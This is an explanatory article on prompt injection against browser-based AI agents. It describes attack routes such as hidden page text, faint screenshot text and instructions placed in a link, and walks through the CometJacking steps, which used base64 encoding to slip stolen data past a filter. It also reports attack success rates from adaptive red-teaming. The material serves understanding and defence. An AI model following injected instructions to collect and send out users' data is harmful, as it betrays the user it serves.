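# Prompt injection against browser-based AI agents and data theft through image URLs and email

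## Browser agents, prompt injection and the same-origin policy

A browser agent is an AI system that reads web pages and can click, type, navigate or call tools in a browser for its user. It often works in the user's own browser, signed in to the user's accounts, on tasks such as filling in forms, comparing products across tabs or working through an inbox. Prompt injection is an attack in which a model receives text as data but follows it as an instruction. An attacker who plants such text on a web page can steer an agent into collecting private data from another tab or account and exfiltrating it, which means moving it to a place where the attacker can read it.

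The same-origin policy is a browser rule that keeps one website from reading another's data. It dates from a time when the pages' own code was the only software moving data between pages. A browser agent can also move data from one site to another, without the browser detecting a violation.

### How a browser agent works

The core of a browser agent is a large language model, a program that takes in a sequence of text (and often images) and produces a continuation. The model cannot open a page by itself. Software around it, usually called a harness, turns the model's output into actions in the browser. The two work in a loop:

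1. The user types a request. The harness places it in the context, which is all the text and images the model has before it when it chooses its next output. The developer's standing instructions are already there.
2. The model writes out an action, such as reading the current page, clicking a link or typing into a box. Developers call this a tool call.
3. The harness performs the action and adds the result to the context. After a read, the result is the content of the page, as text or as a screenshot.
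4. The model chooses again, now from the longer context. The loop repeats until the model writes an answer for the user instead of another action.

Page content enters the same context that holds the user's request and tends to stay there. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026), in *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, describe an interaction history that records the user's instructions, the agent's observations and its responses at every step. The agent needs this record to finish a task that spans several pages, but the record can also keep a card number from a checkout page in the context after the agent has moved to a different site.

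### Assistants that read and agents that act

Some products only summarise a page or answer questions about it, while others also click, type, submit and move between pages. OpenAI's ChatGPT extension for Google Chrome does both, in separate modes. Rijo (2026) reported in *ChatGPT gains control of Chrome tabs to fill forms and send messages* that since an October 2026 update, the Chat mode can gather information from the user's open tabs, while the Work mode can control those tabs to send messages, fill in forms and download files.

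On Android phones in the United States, Gemini in Chrome summarises pages and answers questions for everyone, and subscribers to the more expensive plans also get auto browse, which carries out multi-step web tasks (Sood, 2026, *Android users just got one of Chrome's biggest Gemini upgrades*). In December 2026, Google opened auto browse to its cheaper AI Plus plan in the United States and India (McNeal, 2026, *Chrome's auto browse feature is coming to the cheaper AI Plus tier*).

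Anthropic's *Claude in Chrome is generally available*, from August 2026, describes the browser extension as an agent that reads and types text, clicks links, navigates and fills in forms using the user's existing logins. It can now do so without asking for approval each time. Before each action runs, an automated classifier compares it with the user's request and labels it safe or unsafe.

Product names in this field last a few months, which complicates reading the research. Roesner and Kohlbrenner (2026), in *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy*, tested seven products in January and February 2026, and several of them have since changed:

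- ChatGPT Atlas, OpenAI's own browser, is gone. OpenAI's *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work* set 9 August 2026 as its last day and pointed users to the ChatGPT desktop app and the Chrome extension. International Business Times' *OpenAI Upgrades ChatGPT for Chrome So It Can Read Your Tabs* (2026) confirmed the shutdown in October.
- "Claude for Chrome" is now Claude in Chrome. Its side panel has become a session of Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work, according to Anthropic's *The Claude in Chrome side panel is now Claude Cowork*.
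- Comet, from the AI search company Perplexity, is still on offer. Perplexity now charges separate credits for its browser control, as Cubbins (2026) reported in *Perplexity just gave paying Comet subscribers another huge reason*, and Chen (2026), in *Perplexity hit with class action lawsuit over Comet browser's privacy lapse*, covered a suit over its setting for access to browsing history.
- Microsoft Edge had only limited agent features in the tests, as did Brave and Firefox. In November 2026 Microsoft announced that Copilot Cowork can visit pages and act across several of them from the sidebar of Edge for Business. Customers need a Microsoft 365 Copilot licence and pay by usage, according to 快科技's *微软Edge浏览器彻底变身！微软把AI深度融入* (2026), a Chinese news report on the launch.

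Readers can no longer install Atlas, but experiments on it are still evidence about its design, in which the agent uses the browser much as a person would. That design is more common now than when Roesner and Kohlbrenner ran their tests.

### Direct and indirect prompt injection

The programmer Simon Willison named prompt injection after SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that both attacks have the same underlying cause, which is that trusted and untrusted content are mixed in the same input.

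In direct injection, the attacker types the injected text into the model's input. In an example Willison relays from a paper on secure agent design, a customer asks a car dealer's chatbot for a quote and words the message to extract a large discount. Injection is indirect when the text arrives through a page, email or file. The user is the victim and may never see the text. In Anthropic's example, a user asks Claude to draft replies to some emails, one of which contains a hidden instruction to forward the others to an attacker. Indirect injection is the main danger for browser agents because most of their work is reading strangers' pages.

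Willison distinguishes prompt injection from jailbreaking, in which someone persuades a model to produce output that its vendor has forbidden. He complains that developers who confuse the two tend to dismiss injection as an embarrassment for the vendor. But an indirect attack harms the user whose data the agent can reach.

### Why models cannot reliably tell instructions from data

Software splits text into tokens, which are numbered words or fragments of words, before the model processes it. The developer's instructions, the user's request and the page's content all become tokens in a single sequence. The model uses the whole sequence to compute a probability for every possible next token, and those probabilities are used to choose the agent's next action. A sentence from a web page enters this calculation in the same way as a sentence from the user.

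Developers add markers that show where the user's message ends and a page begins, and they train models to give less authority to text that follows a page marker. But the markers are tokens too. The model learned in training how to respond to them, and nothing in the computation prevents a sentence on a page from raising the probability of an action. A program can prevent SQL injection by sending the database its command and the user's text separately, so that the database never interprets the text as a command. A language model has no second input of that kind. Google's security researchers acknowledge in a 2025 paper, which Willison reviews, that current architectures lack "rigorous separation" between the parts of a prompt.

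Web pages contain many instructions that an agent should follow, so telling the model to ignore all of them would not work, even if the model obeyed perfectly. For example, a delivery form may have a required postcode field that must be filled in before any prices appear, and an agent that ignored this instruction could not finish the order. The model has to judge which instructions serve the user's request, and an attacker can write instructions that appear to serve it.

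In *Agentic Browser Security* (2025), Willison wrote that despite many attempts, nobody had shown a convincing way to distinguish trusted instructions from untrusted content. Models have improved a good deal since then. Anthropic reports that Claude is substantially more resistant to prompt injection than it was in November 2025, but still calls the problem a "moving target". Training can make a model much more resistant without guaranteeing that it will resist every attack, and attackers can keep rewording their text until some version works.

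### Origins and the same-origin policy

Browser makers faced a similar problem well before language models. Web pages contain scripts, small programs that run in the visitor's browser, and a user may have a bank open in one tab and a stranger's page in the next. The same-origin policy is the browser rule that stops scripts from one origin from reading data that belongs to another. An origin is the scheme, host name and port of a web address. For a page $w$, Wang and colleagues write it as

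$$o(w) = (\text{scheme}(w),\ \text{host}(w),\ \text{port}(w)).$$

When a page loads, the browser labels the page's scripts and data with the page's origin. The browser lets a script on page $w_k$ read data from page $w_s$ only if $o(w_k) = o(w_s)$, so all three parts of the origin must match. Suppose the data belongs to `https://mail.example/inbox`. The address doesn't include a port, so the browser assumes 443, the default for https.

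| Address of the page whose script wants to read | Same origin? | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| `https://mail.example/settings` | Yes | Only the path differs, and the path is not part of the origin |
| `http://mail.example/inbox` | No | The scheme is http, which also changes the default port to 80 |
| `https://www.mail.example/inbox` | No | The host name differs |
| `https://mail.example:8443/inbox` | No | The port differs |

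The same-origin policy also applies within a single tab. A malicious page can embed a bank's page in a frame, but Roesner and Kohlbrenner explain that neither page can read the other without the other's explicit permission. The policy doesn't stop a person from copying an account number from one tab and pasting it into another. In its account of their research, the University of Washington notes that users of a standard browser have to carry information between tabs themselves.

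A browser agent fits neither case, because it transfers data automatically, as other software does, but reads pages with the user's own access. *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (2026), by the security consultancy Trail of Bits, points out that agents built into a browser have the same access to data and credentials as the user. Once the agent has read two sites, its context contains content from both, without the browser's origin labels. Wang and colleagues compare injected text to a "script" for the agent, one that the same-origin policy never checks. Computer scientists have long used the term "confused deputy" for a program that an outsider tricks into misusing its legitimate authority. *The Agent Clicks Approve* (2026) cites a taxonomy of web attacks that applies the term to browser agents.

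Roesner and Kohlbrenner conclude that in several of the products they tested, the same-origin policy is only as strong as the agent's defences against prompt injection. The most restrictive designs gave the model limited information about a page in a fixed format, which protected the user better but made the agent much less useful.

### The lethal trifecta

Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for three capabilities that together let an attacker steal data through an agent: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate externally. Removing any one of them prevents this kind of theft, because the agent then has no private data to steal, doesn't read the attacker's instructions, or can't send the data out.

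A logged-in browser agent normally has all three capabilities. The user's sessions give it access to mail, documents and bank accounts. It encounters untrusted content on almost any page with comments, reviews or advertisements. It can communicate outward just by opening a web address, which sends a request to the server's operator, and an agent that acts can also submit forms and write messages. Willison counts even loading an image or showing the user a link to click as outward communication. An email account alone can provide all three capabilities, because it holds private messages, accepts mail from strangers and can send mail to anyone.

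Vendors can shrink one part of the trifecta, but this makes the agent less useful. Anthropic's *Claude gets its own browser in Cowork* describes a separate browser in which Claude never sees the user's tabs, bookmarks or passwords. Users can copy their logins over site by site, and the import leaves out banking, email and single sign-on sites unless the user includes them. Anthropic says that the separate browser carries the same injection risks as any other browser agent, so the benefit is that an injected agent can reach less. For working through an inbox, the company still recommends Claude in Chrome, which uses the accounts the user is already signed in to and so restores the full trifecta. Privilege dropping removes an agent's access or abilities for a task or once it has read untrusted content. It aims to break the trifecta with less loss of usefulness.

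The trifecta is a test only for data theft. An agent that cannot send anything out could still delete a file or place an order on an attacker's instruction. Roesner and Kohlbrenner also found the preconditions for forging actions on other sites and planting false entries in an agent's chat memory.

### Example: a login code in another tab

Suppose a user has two tabs open. One shows an email account that has just received a six-digit login code. The other shows a discussion on a public forum, which the user asks the browser agent to summarise. One of the comments was written by an attacker, who does not run the forum and has no access to the user's computer. In Wang and colleagues' terms, the attacker is a malicious user with partial control of the page, a weaker position than that of a site owner, who controls everything on it.

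The attack begins with injection. The agent reads the discussion to summarise it, the comment enters the context, and the model follows the comment's instruction. The second stage is access, in which the agent switches to the email tab and reads the code into the same context. The last stage is exit, in which the agent sends the code to the attacker. It might open a web address that contains the code, send an email or post a reply on the forum. Each of these is a channel, meaning any observable effect that carries data to the attacker. In 2025, researchers at the browser company Brave demonstrated a very similar attack on Comet, using a Reddit post and a Gmail account.

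A six-digit login code suits an attacker because it holds only about 20 bits of information (a million combinations), which almost any channel can carry. But the code expires quickly, so the attacker has to receive it before then.

The usual web defences give little help here. Forum software can strip scripts from comments, and the same-origin policy would stop any remaining script from reading the mail tab, but this comment is plain text, which the forum is meant to display. The agent opens the mailbox through the user's own session, so the same-origin policy does not block it.

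The attacker needs every stage to work, so the chance of a theft is a product:

$$P(\text{theft}) = P(\text{injection}) \times P(\text{access} \mid \text{injection}) \times P(\text{exit} \mid \text{injection and access}).$$

If, for illustration, a tenth of attempts hijacked the agent, half of those reached the code and half of those got it out, 2.5 per cent of attempts would end in theft. A defence that stops every attempt at any one of these stages is enough to protect the code. An attack success rate is the share of attempts that achieve the attacker's goal, so if a test counts hijacking the agent as the goal, its rate covers only the first stage.

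## How attacker text reaches the agent

Text enters an agent's context from sources including the page on screen, its URL, opened emails and screenshots the harness takes. An attacker who can control text in any of these can attempt an injection. The routes differ in how much the attacker must control and what the user could notice.

| Route | What the attacker must control | What the user sees | What the agent receives |
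|---|---|---|---|
| A page the attacker owns | The whole page, and some way to bring visitors to it | Whatever the attacker chooses, such as an ordinary article | The page's content, often including text that the styling hides |
| A comment, issue or message on another site | An account there, or just a text box | One post among many, on a familiar site | The post together with the site's own text |
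| An advert or embedded frame | The content of one box on the page | An advert or widget | A screenshot includes the box; a text reading may leave it out |
| An email or document | The victim's email address, or a file the victim will open | A normal message or file | The body, sometimes with hidden text |
| An image or screenshot | A picture, or the colours of some text | A picture with nothing to read in it | Words recovered from the pixels |
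| The address of the page | A link that the victim opens | A link, then a normal-looking site or assistant | Instructions inside the address |

### What the routes require

An attacker who owns the page has the most freedom. Brave's *Indirect Prompt Injection remains a fundamental security challenge for AI*, from June 2026, describes a test of Tabstack, a Mozilla service that browses the web for other developers' AI agents. Brave's researchers planted invisible text on a page and asked Tabstack to summarise it. Instead, the agent went to a form on another site, filled it with the conversation so far and submitted it. Mozilla confirmed the flaw within a day and fixed it in under three weeks.

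The owner of a malicious page still has to get agents to visit it. Zscaler's *Indirect Prompt Injection in Web Content Targets AI Agents*, published in July 2026, describes a fake documentation page full of search keywords. An agent looking up a particular Python library was likely to find the page near the top of the search results.

A comment avoids that problem because the site already has readers. In Brave's 2025 attack on Comet, the agent posted the stolen login code as a reply, according to Beebom's *Perplexity's Comet AI Browser Can Be Hijacked Through Malicious Instructions*. Strangers can also write on GitHub, a code-sharing site, and *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents?* (2026) looks for hidden text addressed to AI in its issues, comments and project descriptions. Comments may be a minor route on the open web, however. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Zhang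 and colleagues (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses and traced 78 per cent of the injections they found to the sites' own content. User interactions accounted for 1.4 per cent, although the study's main source, a public web archive, may underrepresent sites that require a login.

Adverts and frames put the attacker's content inside someone else's page. The browser keeps a frame's origin separate from the page around it, but a screenshot merges the two into one picture. The data an injected advert could reach depends on the product. Darinor's *The Same-Origin Policy Is Only as Strong as Your Browser Agent* (2026) reports that an injection on one page could make the agent read another site's data in four of the seven products Roesner and Kohlbrenner studied.

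Advertising networks review adverts before they run, and attackers have begun to target these reviews too. Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, found a scam page for "military glasses" with 24 injection attempts in its code, all meant to make an AI reviewer approve the advert. Unit 42 knows of no confirmed case of this working on a deployed reviewer.

Email is the easiest way to reach a particular person, since the attacker needs only an address. Google (2025) lists emails, documents and calendar invites as carriers of indirect injection. In a laboratory test from August 2026, Gibney hid instructions in the formatting of an email and gave it to a summariser that had no protections (*An Invisible HTML Payload Silently Hijacked Every Email Summarizer Run*). Shared documents add a further difficulty because, as Olejnik notes, a collaborator the user trusts may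 deliver the text.

Attacker text can also reach a model that runs on the user's own computer. Brave also tested Cotypist, a typing assistant for Macs with a local model, and found that instructions in a local document could change its suggestions and bring up the user's credentials. The user had to press a key to accept each suggestion, so the injection could not work without the user's action.

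### The page on screen and the text in the context

A browser builds a page from HTML, which holds the text and its structure, and from style rules, which set each element's colour, size and position and can hide it entirely. A person sees only the finished page. A harness may give the model plain text extracted from the HTML, a structured snapshot listing the page's elements, or a screenshot, and each format leaves out different things.

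Saxton (2026), in *Hidden prompts in web content*, tested this with a fake council page about bin collections. It contained six instructions for AI assistants, hidden in different ways. The text extractors ignored the style rules, so four of the six reached the model as ordinary page text:

- text in a block that the browser was told not to display;
- white text on a white background;
- text in an element one pixel in size;
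- a note in plain view.

The extractors dropped the other two, which were in an HTML comment (a programmer's remark that browsers never display) and an image's written description. A screenshot would have captured only the visible note.

Khodayari and colleagues loaded pages in Chrome and checked whether a visitor could see the injected text. About 87 per cent of the 15,387 injections were not visible. Within the page itself, the most common ways to hide text were giving it low contrast with the background (2,397 injections), covering it with another element (1,860) and placing it outside the visible area (1,802).

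The 87 per cent figure may not hold for browser agents. Just over half of all the injections were in HTTP headers, the technical lines a server sends ahead of a page. Crawlers may process them, but an agent that works from page text or screenshots does not normally receive them. The study also counts text as hidden when its contrast ratio is below 4.5 to 1, a common accessibility threshold, although many people can read text somewhat below it.

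The format in which a page reaches the model also affects how often the model follows injected instructions. When Khodayari and colleagues asked 13 models to summarise pages containing a sample of these injections, the models followed 3.9 per cent of them in plain text and 1.1 per cent in structured snapshots. Plain text discards the signs that a sentence was hidden, so the sentence looks like part of the article.

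### Faint text in a screenshot

Brave's researchers reported a prompt injection flaw in Comet on 1 October 2025 and published it on 21 October. Comet let users take a screenshot of a page and ask questions about it. In *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, Chaikin and Sahib describe writing instructions in faint light blue on a yellow background. A person would not notice them, but software can recover the words from very small differences in pixel colour.

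In the demonstration, the user took a screenshot of a page with a picture of a yellow wall and asked who the author was. Comet extracted the faint text from the image and passed it to the model without separating it from the user's question. Chaikin and Sahib suspect that Comet used optical character recognition to extract the text, but they could not confirm this because Comet's code is not public.

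According to Willison's *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots*, the instructions were for the agent to open the user's Perplexity account page, find the email address there, and open a URL on another website that included the email address. The attack went from one site to the user's account on a second, then sent data to a third. An attacker could use the same sequence to steal more valuable data.

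In a product where screenshots are optional, this route is limited because it works only when the user takes one, but an agent that navigates by screenshots takes them constantly. Filters that inspect a page's HTML also cannot find text that exists only as pixels.

### Why removing hidden text is not enough

A harness can apply the page's style rules and discard whatever a visitor would not see. This would have stopped three of the four instructions that reached Saxton's model, and it costs little compared with retraining a model. It also makes the agent somewhat less useful, because legitimate pages hide text too, such as collapsed menus and labels for people who use screen readers.

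Attackers can also adapt to filters. The scam page that Unit 42 examined used a script to decode its instructions after a delay, when a first scan would already have finished. Another script drew words onto a canvas, so they appeared as an image and not as readable HTML text. To evade keyword filters, the page also split a command across several elements and put invisible characters inside words.

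A filter for hidden text does not stop instructions in plain view. Chaikin and Sahib found that Fellou, another AI browser, partly resisted hidden instructions but treated visible page content as trusted. The user only had to ask Fellou to go to the attacker's page, not to summarize it. According to Willison, the page contained instructions to send the title of the user's latest email to the attacker's site, and the agent opened Gmail to read that title.

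Studies differ on how common visible injections are. Visible text was the most common delivery method in Unit 42's security monitoring data, at 37.8 per cent, while Khodayari and colleagues could confirm only 236 visible injections. Their data also included thousands of header injections that visitors could not see. Even visible injections can go unnoticed, as with one that Unit 42 found in a page footer, where few people read.

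### CometJacking: instructions in a link

In 2025, the security firm LayerX found that a link could attack Comet without any malicious page content, and named the attack CometJacking. Web addresses can end in a query string, a list of values such as search terms. Perplexity accepted whole questions in the query string, so a link could open a conversation with the question already asked. Olejnik explains that the assistant treated a click on the link as if the user had typed the text.

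The attack had five steps:

1. The victim clicked a link in an email or on a website, or a page redirected the browser to it.
2. Comet read part of the query string as a request. LayerX found that an unrecognised value elsewhere in the string made the assistant consult its memory instead of searching the web.
3. The assistant collected private data, such as emails it had helped to write, or messages and appointments from a connected Gmail or Google Calendar account.
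4. It converted the data to base64, a standard way of writing any data with 64 ordinary characters.
5. It sent the result to the attacker's server.

The fourth step, base64 encoding, defeated Perplexity's check on outgoing data. Base64 turns "Tuesday" into "VHVlc2RheQ==", so a filter that searches for recognisable private information finds nothing. The attacker then decodes the data, which requires no key. Making the filter check for base64 would help only until an attacker asked for a different encoding, and a language model can produce many.

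LayerX built one link that stole emails and another that stole calendar invitations. It reported the flaw to Perplexity on 27 August 2025, but Perplexity saw no effect on security and marked the report "Not Applicable". The Hacker News (2025) covered the attack that October. Schneier (2025), in *Prompt Injection in AI Browsers*, quotes a press account that says the attack is possible without user interaction, but LayerX's description requires a click or a redirect. LayerX sells browser security and had an interest in a dramatic finding, but its demonstration sent private email to an outside server, which is hard to reconcile with Perplexity's verdict.

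CometJacking also gets past defences that mark page content as untrusted, because the attacker's text arrived in the place reserved for the user's own words, not in a page. Unit 42 lists a related method called HashJack, which puts instructions after the # sign in a legitimate site's address. Browsers do not send that part of the address to the site, so its server cannot filter it.

### What the injected text has to achieve

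To steal data, an attacker needs injected text that makes the agent take several actions in the right order, whereas spoiling a summary only requires getting the model to write something else.

Injected instructions are more likely to work if the actions they request look relevant to the user's task. The attacker does not see the user's request but can often guess it, because people commonly ask an assistant to summarise the page they are on. Brave's text for Tabstack presented the attacker's form as the place to get the summary, and in its recorded reasoning, the agent treated the visit as the next step of its task. Zscaler's fake documentation page described a payment as the way to fix a missing licence. Attackers can also change what the task appears to be. In *AI browsers were tricked into revealing passwords with a shockingly simple approach*, Horne (2026) reports that LayerX disguised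 a request for sensitive data as part of a game, and that all six AI browsing tools it tested gave data away.

The injected text must also describe the data the attacker wants. A description such as "the latest email" is enough, because the agent searches for the data itself. An attacker who knows nothing about the victim can still guess that a Gmail account is open in the browser.

Finally, the text has to name a destination that the attacker can read, such as a web server, a form or a public comment thread. An attacker can present the theft as a summary or a game, but the destination is harder to disguise because the data has to arrive there.

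### Injections on the live web in 2026

Several groups searched the public web for injections in 2026. The largest study with published counts, by Khodayari and colleagues, found injections on 11,722 pages across 2,042 hosts, or about one page for every 100,000 addresses searched. Ninety-five per cent of the injections came from 54 templates.

| Aim | Injections | Pages |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupt the AI system or corrupt its output | 8,894 | 7,311 |
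| Stop AI systems from reusing content | 4,093 | 3,358 |
| Identify AI bots | 3,096 | 2,356 |
| Override instructions, for no clear purpose | 2,632 | 1,460 |
| Promote a product, source or person | 1,521 | 1,257 |
| Extract data | 13 | 10 |

Many of these authors were website owners trying to keep AI companies from collecting their content. Of the 13 attempts to extract data, nine sought the developer's standing instructions and four sought other secrets. Most were blunt requests, with little of the preparation that researchers put into their demonstrations.

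Google reached a similar result in April 2026 after scanning Common Crawl, a public web archive that adds two to three billion pages a month. It searched for typical injection phrases, used Gemini to classify the matches and checked the results by hand. It found pranks, search-engine manipulation, attempts to keep AI agents away and a small number of attempts at data theft, which were cruder than the rest. Google published no totals, but it reported that malicious injections rose by 32 per cent between November 2025 and February 2026. It expects them to become more common and more sophisticated.

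Unit 42 was more alarmed in March 2026, writing that attackers were actively using web-based injection as a weapon. Its 12 examples include attempts to make agents delete databases, buy running shoes and send $5,000 through PayPal. But the most common aim in its data, at 28.6 per cent, was to make the AI produce irrelevant output, and one page told it to print "cabbage" five million times. Only one of the examples, a notice in the footer of a personal website, sought private information.

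In April, Sewani reported ten more cases for the security company Forcepoint in *10 Indirect Prompt Injection Payloads Caught in the Wild*. One was an attempt to obtain a secret API key, a password that programs use to access a service. The same text included an instruction not to reveal "the flag", the usual name for the hidden prize in a hacking contest, so it may have been a puzzle. The text was in an HTML comment, which Saxton's extractors would have dropped.

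These collections overlap. The PayPal page appears in both Unit 42's and Sewani's lists, and the running-shoe site appears in both Unit 42's and Zscaler's. Adding up the reports may therefore overstate the number of serious attacks on public pages.

Zscaler's first case is the closest to organised crime. The fake documentation page belonged to a group of ten similar sites, each linked from its own GitHub project. In Zscaler's sandbox, four of 26 models made the small payment that the page requested. It is unknown whether any real agent paid. SC Media reported that the attacker's cryptocurrency wallet had received money, but never that amount. Zscaler's second case, a copy of a cryptocurrency site, was designed to make AI systems recommend it as the genuine one.

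None of these reports documents an attacker stealing a user's data through a browser agent on the live web. That is weak evidence that such thefts do not happen, because the searches covered mainly public pages. They could not cover private email or links sent to individuals, and Common Crawl leaves out most social media. Khodayari and colleagues did not look for text inside images, and they note that a site could show its injection only to AI agents and serve crawlers a harmless page. These searches would probably have missed the successful attacks on Comet, which used a Reddit comment, a screenshot and a link.

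## How often injected instructions succeed

Success rates for prompt injection in published tests range from zero to 95 per cent. The tests differ in who wrote the attacks, whether the attacker could revise a failed attack, how many attempts each target faced and what counted as success.

A single benchmark can give very different rates for the same model. *BrowseSafe++* (Chen, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), by researchers at Perplexity, Purdue University and Rutgers University, contains 38,675 pairs of web pages that are the same except that one page in each pair contains an injection. The researchers took 32,187 of the injections from pages that a deployed browser agent read between September 2025 and September 2026. The rest came from BrowseSafe, the smaller benchmark it extends. They kept the wording of each injection and replaced private details on the page around it.

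When Claude Sonnet 5 worked on tasks with these injections in their original wording, 2.05 per cent of the attacks achieved the attacker's goal. In a separate test, a second model judged only whether the agent's answer or tool calls followed the injection, and Sonnet 5 did so on at least 19.74 per cent of pages. The tenfold gap is approximate because the tests used different samples, but counting the first step gives a higher rate because an agent can start following an instruction without achieving the attacker's goal. When the attacker had up to 64 attempts at each task, starting with the original injection and rewriting it after each failure, the rate for achieving the goal rose from 2.05 to 30.66 per cent.

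### Results for Claude, GPT and Gemini

In late 2025, Anthropic tested its browser agent against an automated attacker that adapted its injected instructions and had 100 attempts in each test environment. The success rates are shares of all attempts, so they don't show in how many environments at least one attempt succeeded.

| Model | Model alone | With earlier safeguards | With improved safeguards |
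|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 13.8% | 10.7% | 2.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 13.8% | 10.8% | 1.9% |
| Claude Haiku 4.5 | 12.0% | 11.1% | 2.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 8.0% | 7.6% | 1.4% |

The improved safeguards made more difference than the choice of model. Even Haiku 4.5, the weakest of the four with these safeguards, did better than Opus 4.5 without them.

Attacks on later models had success rates close to zero. *Prompt Injection Robustness*, a summary of Anthropic's results, lists one success in 148 against Claude Mythos Preview in a browser without safeguards. For Claude Opus 5 in Anthropic's own software, the technology news site The Decoder reported no successes in 129 browser scenarios. That result doesn't rule out a low success rate, because if attacks worked in 2.3 per cent of such scenarios, a test of 129 would still record no successes about one time in 20.

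For a later round of browser tests, Anthropic generated the attacks by testing an older model, Opus 4.7, and then applied them to newer ones. The system card for Claude Fable 5.1, a safety report from September 2026, describes this method. The attacker therefore could not adapt to the newer models, but the attacks still succeed against them when the additional safeguards are off.

Anthropic uses a benchmark from the security firm Gray Swan for comparisons between companies. People in public contests wrote the attacks, and Gray Swan selected 1,804 that worked across many models. The benchmark's 37 scenarios cover coding, tool use and control of a graphical desktop. The attacks are meant to cause harmful actions, such as sending out private data or making a payment.

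Without safeguards specific to injection, Fable 5.1 followed 0.1 per cent of single attempts. Given 15 attempts, attackers succeeded 1.0 per cent of the time overall and 4.1 per cent of the time on the graphical desktop, the setting most like a browser. Among other companies' models, Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash did best, at 9.2 per cent after 15 attempts, and most were between 24 and 53 per cent. Anthropic reports these comparisons itself, but leaves out models that the contestants had attacked directly, because that alone would make their scores worse.

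Scores from different editions of the benchmark are not comparable. The Decoder reported an attack success rate of 2.0 per cent for Opus 5 after 15 attempts. In the Fable 5.1 report, which includes nine more scenarios and 670 more attacks, the same model's rate was 4.8 per cent.

Claude Opus 5.5 performed as well as Opus 5 or better on every injection evaluation in Anthropic's *System Card* (2026). According to Digital Matters' *Claude Opus 5.5 Prompt Injection* (2026), the model resists injected instructions from web pages and tools better than before, but is worse at resisting those in text that users paste in themselves. The CometJacking links also put an attacker's words in the user's message.

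OpenAI reports direct and indirect injection separately, and its models fail far more often on indirect attacks. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* gives August 2026 results in which GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05 per cent of direct attacks and 3.77 per cent of indirect ones. *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense* (Cross, 2026) gives October figures for GPT-6 Sol of 99.99 per cent resistance to direct attacks and 97.13 per cent to indirect ones, so 2.87 per cent of indirect attacks succeeded. The indirect figure is the relevant one for a browser agent, but, as TechRepublic notes, it is a share of test attempts, not the probability of a breach in real use.

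### Attackers that learn from failure

A fixed set of attacks measures resistance to texts that already exist, while a real attacker can see that a text failed and write another. Chen and colleagues built a second test, BrowseSafe-Adapt, around this difference:

1. The system puts the original injection on a page and runs the agent on an ordinary user task.
2. A verifier checks the agent's answer, and any changes in the test applications, against the attacker's goal.
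3. If the attack failed, one model reviews what the agent did and works out why.
4. Another model rewrites the injection, and the agent starts again from the same state.

The researchers tested this against seven agents on 1,024 tasks. The original injections achieved their goals on 0.49 to 4.00 per cent of tasks. After up to 64 attempts, the rate rose to 65.23 per cent for GPT-5.5, 92.87 per cent for Gemini 3.1 Pro and 95.41 per cent for Kimi K2, an open-weight Chinese model. Sonnet 5 was the most resistant of the seven. The test did not include Opus 5.5 or GPT-6.

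Some of these attacks only had to change the agent's answer. Others had to change something in an application, as sending a message does, so their success rate is probably a closer measure of the risk of theft. They succeeded less often, at 7.90 per cent for Sonnet 5 and 28.52 per cent for GPT-5.5, but still reached 83.51 per cent for Gemini 3.1 Pro.

Anthropic's results show how much an attack's success depends on the attacker's skill. Gray Swan trained an automated attacker, Shade, on 40 coding scenarios, then tested it on the same ones, with 200 attempts at each. Gray Swan later trained a stronger version for longer and on more varied attacks. The table gives the share of attempts that succeeded against models with extended thinking on. "Probes" are safeguards that check the result of each tool call for injected instructions before the model acts on it.

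| Model | Earlier Shade, no probes | Earlier Shade, probes | Stronger Shade, no probes | Stronger Shade, probes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% | 2.05% | 56.87% | 12.80% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 9.70% | 2.42% | 86.87% | 34.09% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% | 0.39% | 90.93% | 18.21% |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.3% | 0.09% | 19.47% | 15.76% |

The attack success rate against Opus 5 rose from 2.68 to 90.93 per cent with no change to the model. The order of the models changed too, so the earlier test was not a reliable guide to which model was safer. The probes lowered the rates, but the stronger Shade still succeeded in at least 35 of the 40 scenarios against every model in the table.

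All the successful attacks on Fable 5.1 by the stronger Shade were on responses from an older model, Opus 4.8. A classifier for dangerous cybersecurity requests had passed many of Fable 5.1's coding tasks to that model. None of the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself led to a successful attack. The classifier, a safeguard against cybersecurity misuse, had increased the risk from prompt injection, and Anthropic says it is working on the interaction.

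Anthropic regards the Shade tests as harsher than real conditions because the attacker practised on the same scenarios it was scored on. A real attacker usually does not know the details of the target deployment, and repeated attempts make detection more likely. The tests also involve coding, so their percentages do not apply to browsers. But they are a reason to be cautious about any low success rate measured with a fixed set of attacks, including the browser results.

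### Training a model to resist

OpenAI uses an automated attacker to train its models as well as to test them. *GPT-Red* (2026) describes an attacker model that learned to write injections through self-play, training at the same time as a group of defending models. In each scenario, the attacker controls a specific piece of content, such as an email body or a web page banner. Training rewards the attacker when an injection works, and rewards the defenders when they resist it and still finish the user's task. As the defenders improve, the attacker has to find new methods.

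OpenAI then used GPT-Red's injections to train GPT-5.6. One class of attack imitates the model's own reasoning, so the model may treat the attacker's text as its own earlier conclusion. These attacks succeeded more than 95 per cent of the time against GPT-5.1 and less than 10 per cent against GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI found no loss of general ability and no increase in needless refusals, which suggests that the model did not become harder to attack just by doing less.

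In a copy of a public red-teaming contest, GPT-Red found a working attack on GPT-5.1 in 84 per cent of scenarios, compared with 13 per cent for human contestants. The scenarios were new to GPT-Red. Tests that use only human-written attacks may therefore underestimate what an attacker with a capable model could do.

The 0.05 per cent figure for GPT-5.6 Sol comes from environments outside the training set, but the attacker is the same one whose texts the model trained on. The results for the two versions of Shade suggest that a new attacker could succeed much more often. OpenAI says that scaling up the self-play has uncovered new threats to existing models.

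### Detectors and false alarms

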